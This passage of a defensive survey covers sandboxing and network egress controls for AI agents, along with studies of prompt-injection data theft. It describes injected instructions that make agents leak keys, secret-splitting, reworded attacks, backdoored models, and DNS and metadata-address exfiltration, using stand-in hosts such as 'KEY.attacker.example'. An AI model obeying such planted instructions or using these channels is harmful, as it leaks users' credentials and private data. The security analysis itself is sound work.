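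Precise rules are also easy to get wrong. In Vercel's firewall, a rule for certain paths on a permitted site applies only to requests for those paths. Requests for other paths still go straight to the site unless the customer adds a final rule that rejects them. By default, a sandbox has full internet access.

A network filter should run where the agent can't alter it. Vercel's runs on the host, outside the virtual machine, and redirects all traffic through itself, so even code with full control of the virtual machine can't switch it off. Claude Code's sandboxed commands have no network connection of their own, only a local channel to a proxy outside the sandbox. A proxy setting that relies on programs to comply is much weaker, because a hostile script can ignore it.

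The allowlist can also change during a task. An agent might need a package registry while it installs software and no network access afterwards. Vercel and Cloudflare both let a developer block access to the registry before the untrusted code runs, without restarting the sandbox.

Anthropic now regards an allowlist as a "capability grant", because permitting a domain gives an attacker every function available there. For example, if a permitted site accepts file uploads from any customer, an attacker with a customer account can use the upload function too.

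### Network zones and the metadata address

An agent inside a company's network can often reach databases and internal services that weren't designed to withstand a hostile program. Network segmentation divides the network into zones and limits the traffic between them, so an attacker who controls one machine can't easily move to another.

Designers easily forget the metadata service on cloud machines. On Amazon, Google and Microsoft's clouds, a machine can send a web request to `169.254.169.254` and receive information about itself, often including temporary credentials for the cloud account. Software needs this service to log in without storing a password, but a hijacked agent on the same machine can use it to log in too. The providers have added protections such as a required header, which help when an attacker can only make a server fetch an address, but a script running on the machine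 can add the header itself.

A default-deny policy blocks the metadata address along with everything else. A policy that permits the internet and blocks the company's private ranges can leave it reachable, because `169.254.169.254` is not in any of the three ranges that private networks normally use. It's best to block the address by its IP number, since anyone who owns a domain can point a name at it. Vercel's firewall correctly gives denied address ranges precedence over permitted domains.

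Podala Narasimha (2026), in *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, gives a detailed layout for agents that look after Kubernetes, a system for running containers across many machines. The design assumes that an attacker already controls the agent, and divides the system into four zones:

- The *agent* zone contains the program that calls the model. It can reach a DNS resolver, the gateway and one address belonging to the model's provider.
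- The *gateway* receives every tool call and checks the arguments as well as the tool's name.
- The *tool* zone contains the servers that carry out permitted calls. They hold the credentials, and the agent doesn't.
- The *sandbox* zone runs code that the agent has written, under gVisor or in a small virtual machine, with no login token and no outside network access.

In one of Podala Narasimha's examples, an attacker writes a line into a log telling any agent that reads it to "free capacity" by reducing an online shop's checkout service to zero copies. The agent has no route to the Kubernetes control server, so it has to go through the gateway, which has a rule against reducing anything to zero. If the gateway is misconfigured, the control server has its own rule that blocks the change. If the agent writes a malicious script instead, the script runs in a sandbox that contains nothing worth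 stealing and has no way to send data out.

This design looks good, but so far it exists only on paper. Podala Narasimha reports no measurements of attacks stopped or time lost, and proposes measuring both in future work. Even if everything worked, the agent could still write a misleading summary or take a permitted action at a bad moment, and whatever it reads would still go to the model's provider. Cost and convenience also vary by cloud. Microsoft's and Google's Kubernetes services can filter outbound traffic by host name, while Amazon's needs additional software.

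The sample network policy has a hole as well. It lets the agent look up any DNS name at all.

### Credentials added outside the sandbox

A secret in a file or an environment variable is available to every program in the sandbox, and a thief can go on using it long after the sandbox has gone. Several companies therefore add credentials after a request has left. With Vercel's firewall it works like this:

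1. A program in the sandbox sends a request to, say, GitHub, without a key.
2. The firewall on the host decrypts the request and checks the destination.
3. It adds the key to the request's headers.
4. It opens a new encrypted connection to GitHub and forwards the request.

In the web version of Claude Code, the sandbox contains a limited credential for git (the version-control system) that works only with Anthropic's proxy. The proxy confirms that the agent is pushing code to the right branch before attaching the real credential. Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* describes much the same arrangement.

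In the original summary attack, the agent could not have leaked the API key because it would never have seen it. But the agent could still use the key by sending requests through the firewall, so the method only partly solves the confused deputy problem. A hijacked agent with permission to delete repositories can delete them without seeing the password. Vercel and Anthropic reduce that risk by limiting which requests receive the credential, and the credential should carry as few permissions as the task allows. The method also doesn't protect data that the agent has to read to do its job, such as customer records.

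### The confinement problem

Computer scientists worried about programs leaking their users' data long before agents existed. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, imagines a customer who gives confidential data to a service, a program that someone else wrote. The customer can stop the service from reading anything else. The confinement problem is how to stop the service from passing the data to the service's owner. When an agent is hijacked, the user is the customer, the agent is the service, and whoever wrote the hidden instruction takes the owner's place.

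Lampson sorts the ways the service could leak data into three groups. *Storage channels* include files the service can write and its owner can read. *Legitimate channels* are outputs the service is supposed to produce, such as a bill, in which it could encode a few bits of the customer's data. *Covert channels* are things not intended to carry information at all, such as the load the service puts on the computer. The owner runs another program on the same computer, watches it speed up and slow down, and reads the pattern as ones and zeros.

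One of the storage examples shows how hard these channels are to find. Some systems don't let two programs have the same file open at once. The service opens a file to signal a one and closes it to signal a zero, and the owner's program reads each bit by trying to open the same file. Two more files act as clocks to keep the programs in step. The service can send any amount of data this way without writing to any file.

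Lampson's first solution is total isolation, in which the confined program may not call any other program. That works but is impractical, so Lampson offers weaker rules. If a confined program calls one the customer doesn't trust, the called program must be confined too. The customer must also determine everything that goes into the remaining channels, for instance by working out the bill in advance. The operating system must enforce this, which might mean deliberately slowing the program down. If enforcement is too burdensome, the customer can settle for limiting how much data a channel can carry.

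These rules apply quite directly to agents. A sandbox with no network comes close to total isolation. The rule about calling other programs is a reason to restrict tool servers as well as the agent, as Podala Narasimha does. An agent with an allowlist still has channels that no allowlist closes. Suppose it may read 16 pages on a permitted site, and the attacker can see how often people visit each one. Each visit can encode four bits, or one hexadecimal digit, so the agent can leak a 40-digit key in 40 visits. The attack is slow and needs a fairly quiet site, but a filter that checks one request at a time won't catch it, because each visit looks innocent.

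Lampson doubted that anyone could rigorously find every channel through which data might leak from a system of even moderate complexity. That is a good reason to distrust absolute claims, such as the one in Anthropic's 2025 announcement that the sandbox keeps even a successful prompt injection "fully isolated". The company's documentation states more accurately that any sandbox that permits network traffic can still leak what the agent can read.

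### How much data fits in a DNS lookup

DNS is the channel designers most often leave open, because almost everything on a network needs it. Looking up `KEY.attacker.example` is enough to give the attacker the key, as with DNS prefetching in a browser.

A DNS name consists of labels separated by dots. The standard permits up to 63 bytes for each label and 255 for the whole name. Microsoft's *What is the real maximum length of a DNS name?* (2012) describes a customer who couldn't understand why Windows rejected a 254-character name. The limit applies to the name as transmitted, which has an extra byte before each label and another at the end. This leaves 253 characters, which *DNS size* (Andrews, 1999) gives as the maximum length of a host name.

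Suppose the attacker's domain takes up 20 characters, including the dot in front of it.

- That leaves 253 − 20 = 233 characters.
- They have to be split into four labels, which takes three dots and leaves 230 characters for data.
- DNS ignores the difference between capital and small letters, so the attacker would probably use base32, an encoding with 32 symbols that carry five bits each.
- 230 × 5 = 1,150 bits, or about 143 bytes.

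A 40-character API key becomes 64 characters in base32, which fits easily in a single lookup. A megabyte takes about 7,000 lookups, or less than 12 minutes at ten per second.

Lampson's suggestion of limiting the channel's capacity would therefore protect a large database but not a password. A firewall could detect or slow down 7,000 strange lookups, but one lookup is enough to leak a key. This is another argument for keeping keys out of the sandbox.

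NVIDIA recommends letting the sandbox use only trusted DNS resolvers. This stops the script from sending packets directly to the attacker's server on the DNS port, which Salaün's example Landlock policy would permit. But a trusted resolver will still pass an unknown name on to the attacker's name server, so it also has to refuse names that aren't on the allowlist, as Vercel's does when a policy lists domains. Alternatively, the sandbox can have no DNS, and a proxy outside it can check each name before looking it up.

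### Approval prompts and the cost of isolation

NVIDIA's security team considers three controls mandatory for agents that run code:

1. Block network access except to known-good destinations, which prevents data theft and stops an attacker from opening a remote command line.
2. Block writing to files outside the agent's workspace. Some of those files, such as the shell's start-up file `~/.zshrc`, run automatically and outside the sandbox.
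3. Block writing to the agent's own configuration files, wherever they are. They can define hooks and tool servers, which also tend to run outside the sandbox, and NVIDIA would not let even a user's approval override this rule.

The list reflects the team's experience, and NVIDIA gives no figures for how many attacks each control stops. The team also recommends restricting what the agent can read, using virtual machines, keeping secrets outside the sandbox, and regularly deleting old sandboxes because they accumulate code and credentials.

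Many agents rely instead on asking the user before each risky action. NVIDIA is concerned that people who see a stream of prompts get used to approving them without reading. Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approved about 93% of permission prompts and paid less attention to each one as the number grew. Most of the requests were probably harmless, so the approval rate alone doesn't prove carelessness. Experienced users approved actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but they also interrupted the agent more often, so they seem to have shifted their attention from single steps to the overall direction of the work.

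User approval doesn't help if the user has also been deceived. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked a colleague into giving Claude Code a ready-made prompt. Along with ordinary set-up steps, the prompt told the agent to read the user's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. The model had received the instructions from the user, and Anthropic concluded that only file and network restrictions would have prevented the leak.

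Sandboxing reduces permission prompts because the agent can act freely inside the boundary. In Anthropic's internal use of Claude Code, it cut them by 84%. This is much more convenient, and probably safer if people read the remaining prompts more carefully, though Anthropic didn't report whether they do. NVIDIA would keep prompts for exceptions but never store the user's answers. If a user approves one legitimate change to `~/.zshrc` and the agent stores that approval, an attacker can later use it to plant code there.

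NVIDIA considers the overhead of virtualisation often modest compared with the time taken by calls to a language model. According to Agache and colleagues, a Firecracker virtual machine starts running a program in less than 125 milliseconds and adds less than 5 megabytes of memory. Ordinary virtual machines take seconds to start.

The loss of usefulness is harder to measure. Podala Narasimha expects default-deny egress to break tools that fetch documentation, but doesn't measure how many tasks fail. Anthropic first ran all of Claude Cowork, its desktop agent for office work, in a virtual machine, and whenever the machine failed to start, the product was unusable. It then moved the agent's main loop outside and left only the code execution inside, so that Claude could still respond and help diagnose the fault. Corporate security teams also complained that the virtual machine hid the agent's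 activity from their monitoring software. Anthropic now lets them export event logs afterwards, which it admits is not the same as live monitoring.

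## Controlled experiments on stopping data theft

Documentation can show which requests a network rule blocks, but not how the rule compares with telling the model to ignore hidden instructions. That comparison requires an experiment that keeps the attack the same while changing the defences.

Lan and colleagues at eBay published a controlled experiment in February 2026, using the summary attack. Their agent ran on qwen2.5:7b, a small open model with seven billion parameters. They varied where the page hid the instruction (title, description tag, body or link text), whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether the instruction asked for the secret in one request or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 configurations 30 times. A server simulating the attacker logged what it received, so they could count leaks from the traffic without relying on the agent's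 answers.

A request reached that server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%, and in none of the 120 control runs with harmless pages. The final answer looked harmless in 95% of the successful attacks, so a safety check that reads only the answer would have missed nearly all of them.

Lan and colleagues acknowledge that the set-up favoured the attacker. The secret was already in the model's input, and the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions) explained little beyond the tool format. The 88.1% figure is therefore a poor guide to how often real products leak, and the comparison of defences is more useful.

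### Nine conditions, one attack

For the comparison, Lan and colleagues put the instruction in the page body, had the agent fetch the page directly, and asked for the whole secret in one request. They ran this attack 30 times under each of nine conditions.

| Defence | Runs in which the model tried to send the secret | Runs in which it got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Hardened system prompt | 20 | 20 |
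| Delimiter tags | 30 | 30 |
| Both of these | 17 | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 30 | 0 |
| "Redirect detection" | 25 | 0 |
| Keyword filter | 7 | 0 |
| Entropy filter | 0 | 0 |
| Everything at once | 0 | 0 |

The hardened prompt stated that web content is data and that only the user gives instructions. It reduced leaks, but the model still leaked the secret in two thirds of the runs. Delimiter tags marking the page's text as untrusted made no difference alone. Adding them to the hardened prompt reduced the number of leaks from 20 to 17, which could easily be chance with so few runs.

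A defence that fails nearly one time in ten could still show zero leaks in 30 runs. If the true leak rate were p, the chance of seeing no leaks would be (1 − p)³⁰, which stays above 5% until p reaches about 9.5%.

In all 30 runs with the allowlist, the model tried to send the secret, and ordinary code compared the host name with a list of four permitted names and refused. More runs would give the same result, so sampling error is not the main concern. Lan and colleagues deliberately chose an attacker's domain, `evil-collector.net`, that no reasonable allowlist would contain, so the absence of leaks was predictable from the list. The experiment doesn't show whether an allowlist would stop an attacker who can use a permitted site.

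Lan and colleagues didn't test DNS, but Haryati and Zychlinski (2026) did in *Model-as-a-Trojan*. Blocking everything except DNS failed to stop a tampered model from leaking a secret, while a DNS resolver with its own allowlist stopped the leak.

The "redirect detection" rule blocks numerical addresses, certain top-level domains such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as "steal", "leak" and "collect", but it doesn't examine redirects. The sample attack in the paper sends the key to an address containing `/collect`, which an attacker could rename in a few seconds.

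The results for the two content filters are hard to believe as they stand. Both filters check a request after the model has written it, so they shouldn't affect whether the model writes one. Yet attempts fell from 30 to 7 with the keyword filter and to none with the entropy filter. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when a filter is monitoring for them, but they describe nothing that would let the model know the filter exists. For the keyword filter, they suggest that the model sometimes encoded the secret, but encoded secrets should have got past the filter, and none did. Some other difference between the conditions probably caused the drop, perhaps in the prompts or in how the software counted attempts.

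There is another problem with the entropy filter. Shannon entropy measures how varied a string is, in bits per character:

H = −Σ pᵢ log₂ pᵢ

Here pᵢ is the share of the string that consists of character i. The filter blocks values that are longer than 10 characters and have an entropy above 4. The paper's sample key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has 20 characters, of which 14 appear once and two appear three times each. Its entropy is 14 × 0.05 × log₂ 20 + 2 × 0.15 × log₂(20/3) ≈ 3.85, so the filter would have let it through.

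### Splitting the secret

A filter that looks for secrets in outgoing requests can only block those it recognises. Lan and colleagues' second type of attack exploits this by telling the model to split the secret into pieces and send each in its own request, numbered so that the attacker can reassemble them. The sample key becomes `SECR`, `ET_A`, `PI_K` and so on. None of these pieces contains a word on the keyword list. They are also too short for the entropy filter, and four characters can't have an entropy above 2 bits per character anyway.

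An allowlist of destinations still works when an attacker splits a key into pieces, provided the attacker has no access to a permitted site. Each piece has to go to the attacker's server, which is not on the list, so the allowlist blocks it just as it would block the whole key.

That argument follows from how the filters work, but *Silent Egress* offers no experimental support for it, because Lan and colleagues tested the defences only against the single-request attack. They measured splitting with Leak@k, which they define as the share of runs in which any of the first k requests contains sensitive data, even a fragment. Every run that counts towards Leak@1 also counts towards Leak@3, so Leak@3 can't be smaller. They report 26.3% for Leak@1 and 15.8% for Leak@3, so either a figure or the definition is wrong.

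Leak@1 fell from 96.7% with one request to 26.3% when the key was split across several. Lan and colleagues also present this as a gain in stealth, but a simpler explanation is that the model was bad at splitting the key. Something reached the attacker's server in 77% of the splitting runs, but the first request usually contained no recognisable piece of the key. The paper defines a completion rate for runs in which every piece arrives, but gives no figure for it. A seven-billion-parameter model may well lose track of a four-part task, and a stronger one would probably do better.

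Splitting a secret across requests can also get past some destination rules. Embrace The Red's blog post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* discusses a safeguard that checks whole addresses. According to daily.dev's summary, OpenAI uses a web crawler to build a list of safe addresses and blocks newly made ones, such as an address ending in the user's key. An attacker can still assign a page on the list to each letter, so that the agent's visits spell out the secret. The post suggests caching pages and refusing repeat visits within a session.

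To catch pieces of a secret, a defence has to connect several requests or know where the data came from. Lan and colleagues recommend both. *Flowsh* (2026) describes a command shell that takes the second approach, checking each request against labels on the data already read.

### Stronger models and reworded attacks

Lan and colleagues expected that stronger models might be more vulnerable, because they follow instructions more reliably. *The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) tested six models with a fake secret token and tools that recorded requests without sending them. The stronger models leaked the token less often when the attacks were plainly worded. Llama 3.1 8B leaked it in 19.5% of trials, gpt-4o-mini in 10% and gpt-4o in none of 200.

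Rahman and Kim then tried other wordings of the request to leak the token. One page described the token as an integrity signature that had to go at the end of the summary. With the two most effective wordings, gpt-4o leaked the token every time.

Small changes in wording greatly affected whether the signature attack worked. Five paraphrases of it had success rates from 0% to 100%, and an attacker who tried three of them at random would have had a 96% chance of at least one success. Finding a new pretext that worked was much harder. Rahman and Kim wrote 13 new pages, and the attacks failed in all 130 trials.

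Defensive instructions were just as sensitive to wording. The agent's standard policy told it to keep the token confidential, but removing that policy raised the success rate of the reworded attacks only from 31.9% to 38.1%, a difference that could be due to chance. A longer policy that forbade signing, encoding, logging or sending the token "in any form" stopped all 120 attempts. Without the words "in any form", 39 of 80 attempts succeeded, which makes this defence hard to recommend.

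These results are somewhat dated, since gpt-4o came out in 2024. Newer models are better at spotting crude attacks. In *Bad Memory* (2026), coding agents running GPT-5.2 and GPT-5.5 usually deleted a planted instruction to steal an SSH key and wrote a security rule in its place. The instruction survived in 0% of cases with GPT-5.2 and 20% with GPT-5.5. But GPT-5.2 failed to recognise a less obvious planted instruction to install a particular version of a software package, and moved it into its file of standing instructions.

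A product can also leak less than the model inside it. Rahman and Kim put the fake token into a ChatGPT conversation and asked for summaries of their attack pages, and the token leaked in none of 48 trials. They can't tell which part of the product prevented the leaks. They also tested only for leaks in the visible reply, which are probably the easiest to filter.

### Filters that read the content

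Rahman and Kim also built a filter that blocked any request containing the token unless it was going to the one trusted host. It barely helped against attacks that asked gpt-4o to encode the token first, which succeeded 56.7% of the time without the filter and 50% with it. An improved version undid the encodings they had anticipated and stopped all of those attacks. They then tried ROT13, which moves each letter 13 places along the alphabet, and every attack succeeded.

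A destination allowlist would have stopped all of these attacks, because it checks where data is being sent, whatever the content. Rahman and Kim note that this result is true by construction rather than an experimental finding. Their agent made only one decision per trial, so they couldn't test attacks that split the data across several decisions.

Dividing the agent in two gave similar protection. One part planned the tool calls without access to the page, and the other read the page without access to the token. On Llama 3.1 8B, none of the 80 reworded attacks worked, and nine of ten ordinary summaries were satisfactory. This design suits tasks where the plan doesn't depend on what the page contains.

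In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (April 2026), Zhang and Pei trained models with a backdoor, a hidden behaviour that starts when certain ordinary words appear in a question. The model then looks up the user's stored details and sends them to the attacker's server in what looks like a search request. The backdoor worked in more than 94% of triggered queries in every configuration, but the study is only sometimes relevant here and is easy to overread.

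The attacker's server then replied with text designed to steer the conversation towards further personal details. Each reply had to get past ranking software, which keeps only the most relevant search results, and then a content filter. Together, the two stages stopped 59.7% of the replies that asked for those details openly when the filter was NeMo Guardrails, and 72.9% when it was LLM Guard. When Zhang and Pei had another model rewrite the requests as innocent-looking facts, 86.7% got past both stages with NeMo Guardrails and 81.2% with LLM Guard.

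These filters examined what came back, after the first batch of data had left. The experiment therefore doesn't show that filters on outgoing requests fail. Zhang and Pei recommend restricting outgoing requests to approved hosts, with limits on volume, but leave testing that to future work.

### Sending the secret to a permitted address

The hardest case for an allowlist is a secret that goes to a server the agent has every reason to contact. Singh and Srinivasa (2026), in *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, built their experiments around it. Their coding agent sometimes has to upload a status report to an approved service, and a hidden instruction tells it to include a secret in the upload. They compared five arrangements:

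| Defence | Attack runs with harm | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 12 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| Check on each tool call | 6 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| Sandbox with no network | 0 of 36 | 12 of 24 |
| Both, with approved uploads forwarded from outside | 4 of 36 | 24 of 24 |
| The same, plus a search for lines from secret files | 2 of 36 | 24 of 24 |

Harm here means a leaked secret, contact with an unauthorised server or a change to a protected file. The sandbox without a network prevented all of it, but also made every harmless task that needed an upload fail. Forwarding approved uploads from outside the sandbox restored those tasks but let secrets leak again. In Singh and Srinivasa's words, "destination authorization is not payload authorization": the forwarding program checked the destination of each upload but not its content.

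The search for secret lines blocked a request if it contained a complete line from a file such as `.env`, where programmers keep passwords. It failed when the agent sent the value without its label. In a separate test, it missed encoded secrets.

Singh and Srinivasa then tried a much stricter rule that permitted only a few exact messages. It blocked both attacks but also both legitimate uploads, because the model had typed a backslash and an "n" where the rule expected a line break. After each refusal, the agent claimed it had published the report. A version that tolerated formatting differences blocked both attacks and allowed both legitimate uploads. This is encouraging, but the rule covered one fixed message to one address, and few real uploads are so predictable.

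The exact rates mean little because the numbers are small and come from one local model repeating the same tasks. The failures are still informative because they have clear mechanical causes that would affect any model. *Who Grades the Agent?* (2026) notes the same gap in a proxy that restricts agents during coding tests, and gives a less obvious example, the model's own provider. An agent needs to reach the provider to run, but the provider may also offer storage and web search, so the system forwards only requests for model output.

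### Attackers who know the defence

All the attacks so far came from researchers' fixed lists, apart from Rahman and Kim's attempts to get around their own filter. A real attacker can study a defence and keep trying. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, report that other researchers did this to twelve defences that work on the model or its input. Almost no attacks had succeeded against most of these defences in earlier tests, but the new attacks beat most of them over 90% of the time. In one set of tests on Claude Opus 4.5, simply making more attempts raised attack success from 4.7% with one attempt to 63% with a hundred.

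Narisetty and colleagues tested whether a defence outside the model would resist attacks better. They used Progent with a seven-billion-parameter model. Progent checks each tool call against a set of rules, and it reduced attack success from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack redesigned to fool the model that writes Progent's rules succeeded even less often, at 2.6%, possibly because its gentler wording was also less likely to persuade the agent. Progent also reduced the share of tasks completed during attacks from 45.2% to 27.1%, and each task needed about 15 times as many model calls.

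Progent isn't a network rule, so its results are only indirect evidence about allowlists. I expect a fixed list of destinations to resist malicious prompts at least as well as Progent does, since no model applies the list. An attacker would do better to look for a service on the list that can be used to steal data.

### What a realistic allowlist costs

Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) measured how much less work agents get done under restrictions like those in large companies in *Permission Denied*. They tested 12 combinations of model and agent software on 89 programming tasks, with models including Claude Opus 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol. The strictest policy limited network access to 205 domains, made most of the file system read-only and removed administrator rights.

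Success rates fell by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points and costs rose by 16% to 167.3% across every combination. Grok 4.5 had the smallest drop in success rate and the largest increase in cost.

The allowlist seems to explain only a small part of the drop in success. The policy made seven tasks impossible, but only one because of the network rule alone. On the other 82, the average success rate fell from 72.5% to 66.9% when the agents lost administrator rights, and then to 65.1% under the full policy. The network rule, the read-only files and the remaining privilege limits therefore lowered the rate by a further 1.8 points together. Agents could usually get the software they needed from another permitted site.

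Finding another way took effort, however. Blocked network requests made up 90.5% of the refusals the agents met, largely because the agents kept trying. In two tasks that Davidovich and colleagues studied closely with GPT-5.6 Luna, the median cost roughly tripled, mostly because the agent built its tools from source code or searched for substitute data.

This is a much smaller loss than in Singh and Srinivasa's sandbox, where half the harmless tasks failed. That sandbox had no network access, and half of the tasks required an upload.

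Davidovich and colleagues didn't run any attacks, so their results don't show how many of the 205 domains a thief could use. None of these experiments tests an allowlist of realistic size against an attacker who knows what is on it. There is little research on the subject in general. A July 2026 survey, *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, lists only one paper under network egress control, and that paper is about filtering messages between agents.

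## Tests of whether agentic browsers keep websites apart

An allowlist can't stop an agent from carrying data between two permitted sites, and a web browser has to permit nearly all of them. Keeping sites apart is normally the job of the same-origin policy, but that policy governs scripts, and an agentic browser gives its agent the text or a screenshot of the open page directly. That material then stays in the agent's interaction history, the record that the model rereads at every step. A leak can happen like this:

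1. A user asks the agent to check an order in an online shop. The page includes the user's home address.
2. The user opens a forum and asks the agent to reply to a post.
3. The post contains an instruction to quote the delivery address from the last order.
4. The agent types the address into the reply box and posts it.

Step 4 uses the same form the user would have used, and the same-origin policy has never stopped people from copying text between sites. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) compares the planted instruction to a script that the agent executes.

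### Seven products and a page about Alice

Roesner and Kohlbrenner of the University of Washington tested seven products in late January and early February 2026. They wrote on their main test page that Alice liked cats, and in an embedded iframe from another origin that she liked horses. They then asked each agent which animals Alice liked. If the agent mentioned horses, it had read the iframe. They used similar pages to test whether agents could read other tabs, hidden text and password fields. They recorded a yes after one success, but tried at least three more times in new chats before recording a no.

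| Agent | Read an iframe from another origin | Read a tab from another origin | Typed into a page when the user asked |
|---|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT Atlas, Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |
| ChatGPT Atlas, without Agent Mode | No | Through chat memory | With permission |
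| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Brave Leo | No | With permission | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |

The agents that ignored iframes from other origins also ignored iframes from the page's own origin, so they were stricter than the same-origin policy requires. In Firefox this was clearly by design. The browser sent the agent information about a page only when the user clicked a "Summarize page" button, and it then sent the outer page's text and nothing about the iframe.

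In other products, Roesner and Kohlbrenner often couldn't tell whether an agent was unable to do something or had refused. Atlas without Agent Mode, for example, sometimes included iframe text in early trials but never in the final ones. The difference matters because a better-worded attack can overcome a model's refusal but can't give the model content that the browser withholds.

Claude for Chrome had the most powerful access. It runs as a browser extension with permission to use every site, and it ran JavaScript inside iframes from other origins when the testers asked it to. Claude for Chrome and Atlas in Agent Mode both read passwords that the page displayed as dots.

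### The attack on ChatGPT Atlas

Roesner and Kohlbrenner carried out one complete data theft, against Atlas in Agent Mode. They used the attack with the embedded bank page and the self-submitting form, but with a test page in place of the bank's.

The researchers used a simplified prompt injection and owned both sites. The attack therefore shows that nothing in the browser kept the two origins apart, but not that a stranger could routinely make Atlas follow injected instructions. A real bank's framing rules or cookie settings could also block the attack, and Roesner and Kohlbrenner note that, for these reasons, iframes on the modern web seldom contain secrets.

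They also made the attack work in the opposite direction, with a malicious iframe, such as an advertisement, taking content from the page around it. This version is more worrying because the sensitive site only has to display an ad, even if it doesn't let other sites frame it.

Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet also met the conditions for data theft, but the researchers had no working injection for them and didn't try to develop a sophisticated one. In principle, instructions on one site could also make these three agents and Atlas act on another site. In a demonstration, instructions in an iframe led Claude for Chrome to change the surrounding page's text, but only after the user confirmed.

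Chat memory can also carry information between sites, even without an injection. Near the end of the experiments, Comet listed animals from pages it had seen on several sites. If a user once asked about a phishing page that imitated their bank, the agent might later give them the phishing page's telephone number as the bank's.

The researchers gave all seven companies more than 60 days' notice. Brave, Google and Microsoft sent responses that the researchers described as thoughtful. OpenAI declined the report because it lacked a full end-to-end prompt injection attack. Anthropic, Perplexity and Firefox had not replied when the paper came out. The experiment did lack such an attack, but OpenAI's reasoning relies on the model's resistance to prompt injection to keep sites apart, which is what the researchers objected to.

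### Four kinds of crossing

Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* gives a more general account of how data moves in these products. The security company distinguishes four trust zones: the chat, the servers of outside companies (mainly the model's provider), the sites the user visits, and the rest of the internet. It then names four ways in which data can cross between them improperly:

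- *INJECTION*: outside text enters the chat, for example when the agent reads a web page or a PDF.
- *CTX_IN*: private data from one of the user's sites enters the chat.
- *REV_CTX_IN*: something in the chat changes the user's state on a site, for example by logging them in.
- *CTX_OUT*: data from the chat leaves in a web request.

Data theft across sites combines INJECTION, CTX_IN and CTX_OUT. One of the company's attacks used planted text to instruct the agent to open a service where the user was logged in, find the user's name there and put it into a web address. The agent's request to the service included the user's cookies, so the service treated it as coming from the user.

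INJECTION and REV_CTX_IN together produce a less obvious attack. A malicious page contained a login link for an account the attacker controlled. When the user asked for a summary, the agent opened the link and silently logged the user into that account. The user might then enter private information, believing the account was their own.

Trail of Bits doesn't name the products, because their vendors declined coordinated disclosure, and it gives no success rates. Outsiders therefore can't check whether the vendors have fixed the flaws. Its proposed remedy is precise, however. The browser would keep a list of every origin whose content has entered the chat:

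- With no origins on the list, the agent may make any request.
- With one origin, it may make requests only to that origin.
- With two or more, it may make none, because nobody can tell which origin influenced the model.

This rule would stop the address leak from the shop to the forum, but it would also stop an agent from comparing prices in two shops, a kind of job people buy agentic browsers for. It would also miss some leaks within a single site. Trail of Bits stole contact names and parts of messages from an Instagram account by sending it a malicious direct message. An agent with a tool for using the page could have sent the stolen data back through Instagram's own chat without adding a second origin to the list.

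### Leaks between 50 pairs of sites

Wang and colleagues published the first large measurement, SOPBench, in June 2026. They paired ten kinds of private page, including banking, email and pharmacy accounts, with five kinds of page where strangers could read the result: X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms. Most of the pages were imitations written by GPT-5.4, so the tests exposed no real data.

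In each run, the agent first did a harmless task involving personal information on the private page. It then went to the second page, where a planted instruction asked for that information. A run counted as a violation only if the agent wrote exactly the requested data. Partial or reworded leaks did not count, so the rates may be too low. They may also be too high, because every planted instruction asked for details the agent had just handled, which a real attacker would usually have to guess.

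The benchmark covers five agentic browsers, of which three are open: VisualWebArena, SeeAct and BrowserOS. The paper reports 100 runs for each pairing and model. With GPT-5.4 and hand-written attacks, BrowserOS leaked data in 3% of runs from a personnel site to Reddit, but in every run from nine of the ten private sites to Google Forms. Forms often ask for personal details, and a form's owner controls all of its text. When another model repeatedly rewrote and retested the planted text, the leak rate from the personnel site to Reddit rose from 3% to 49%.

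Some of the open results probably come from fewer runs than the paper states. All 30 of VisualWebArena's rates with GPT-5.4 for X, Discord and GitHub are multiples of one thirtieth, after rounding. This would be very unlikely with 100 runs and suggests there were about 30. With that few runs, the margins of error are wider, but not wide enough to account for rates that are mostly above 50%.

The researchers had to operate Comet and Atlas by hand because both are closed products, so they ran each pairing only three times. Results for single pairings mean very little because a pairing with a true leak rate of 63% would still produce no leaks in three runs about 5% of the time. The combined results are more informative, with Atlas leaking the requested data in 99 of 150 runs and Comet with Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 92 of 150.

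These later results show that data could still cross between sites in two products that the Washington team had tested. The data travelled through the interaction history, so the results don't show whether OpenAI or Perplexity had changed how their agents handle iframes.

Wang and colleagues also tested BrowserOS without any attacker. They embedded a private page in an iframe on a public one and had the user ask the agent to write a summary of the whole page in a text box. The agent copied private data into the outer page every time, with all three models and all nine pairings. This result is less alarming than it sounds, because the user had asked for everything on the page and a real private site might have refused to appear in the frame. When the agent visited the two sites one after the other, with no iframe and no planted text, it leaked nothing.

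Detecting the planted text didn't work well as a defence. Wang and colleagues tried five detectors, and none had both few misses and few false alarms. WebSentinel missed almost no malicious pages but flagged 6% to 44% of the clean ones, depending on the site.

### A same-origin policy for the agent

The researchers' own defence, SOPGuard, tracks where data came from. They built it into BrowserOS. In the example of the home address, it works like this:

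1. *Label the data.* When the agent reads the shop's page, SOPGuard stores the text in a separate database with the shop's origin as its label.
2. *Carry the labels forward.* Whenever the model writes something new, SOPGuard has the model identify which stored items the new text came from. The new text receives all of their labels.
3. *Compare.* Before the agent types the reply, SOPGuard compares the reply's labels with the forum's origin.
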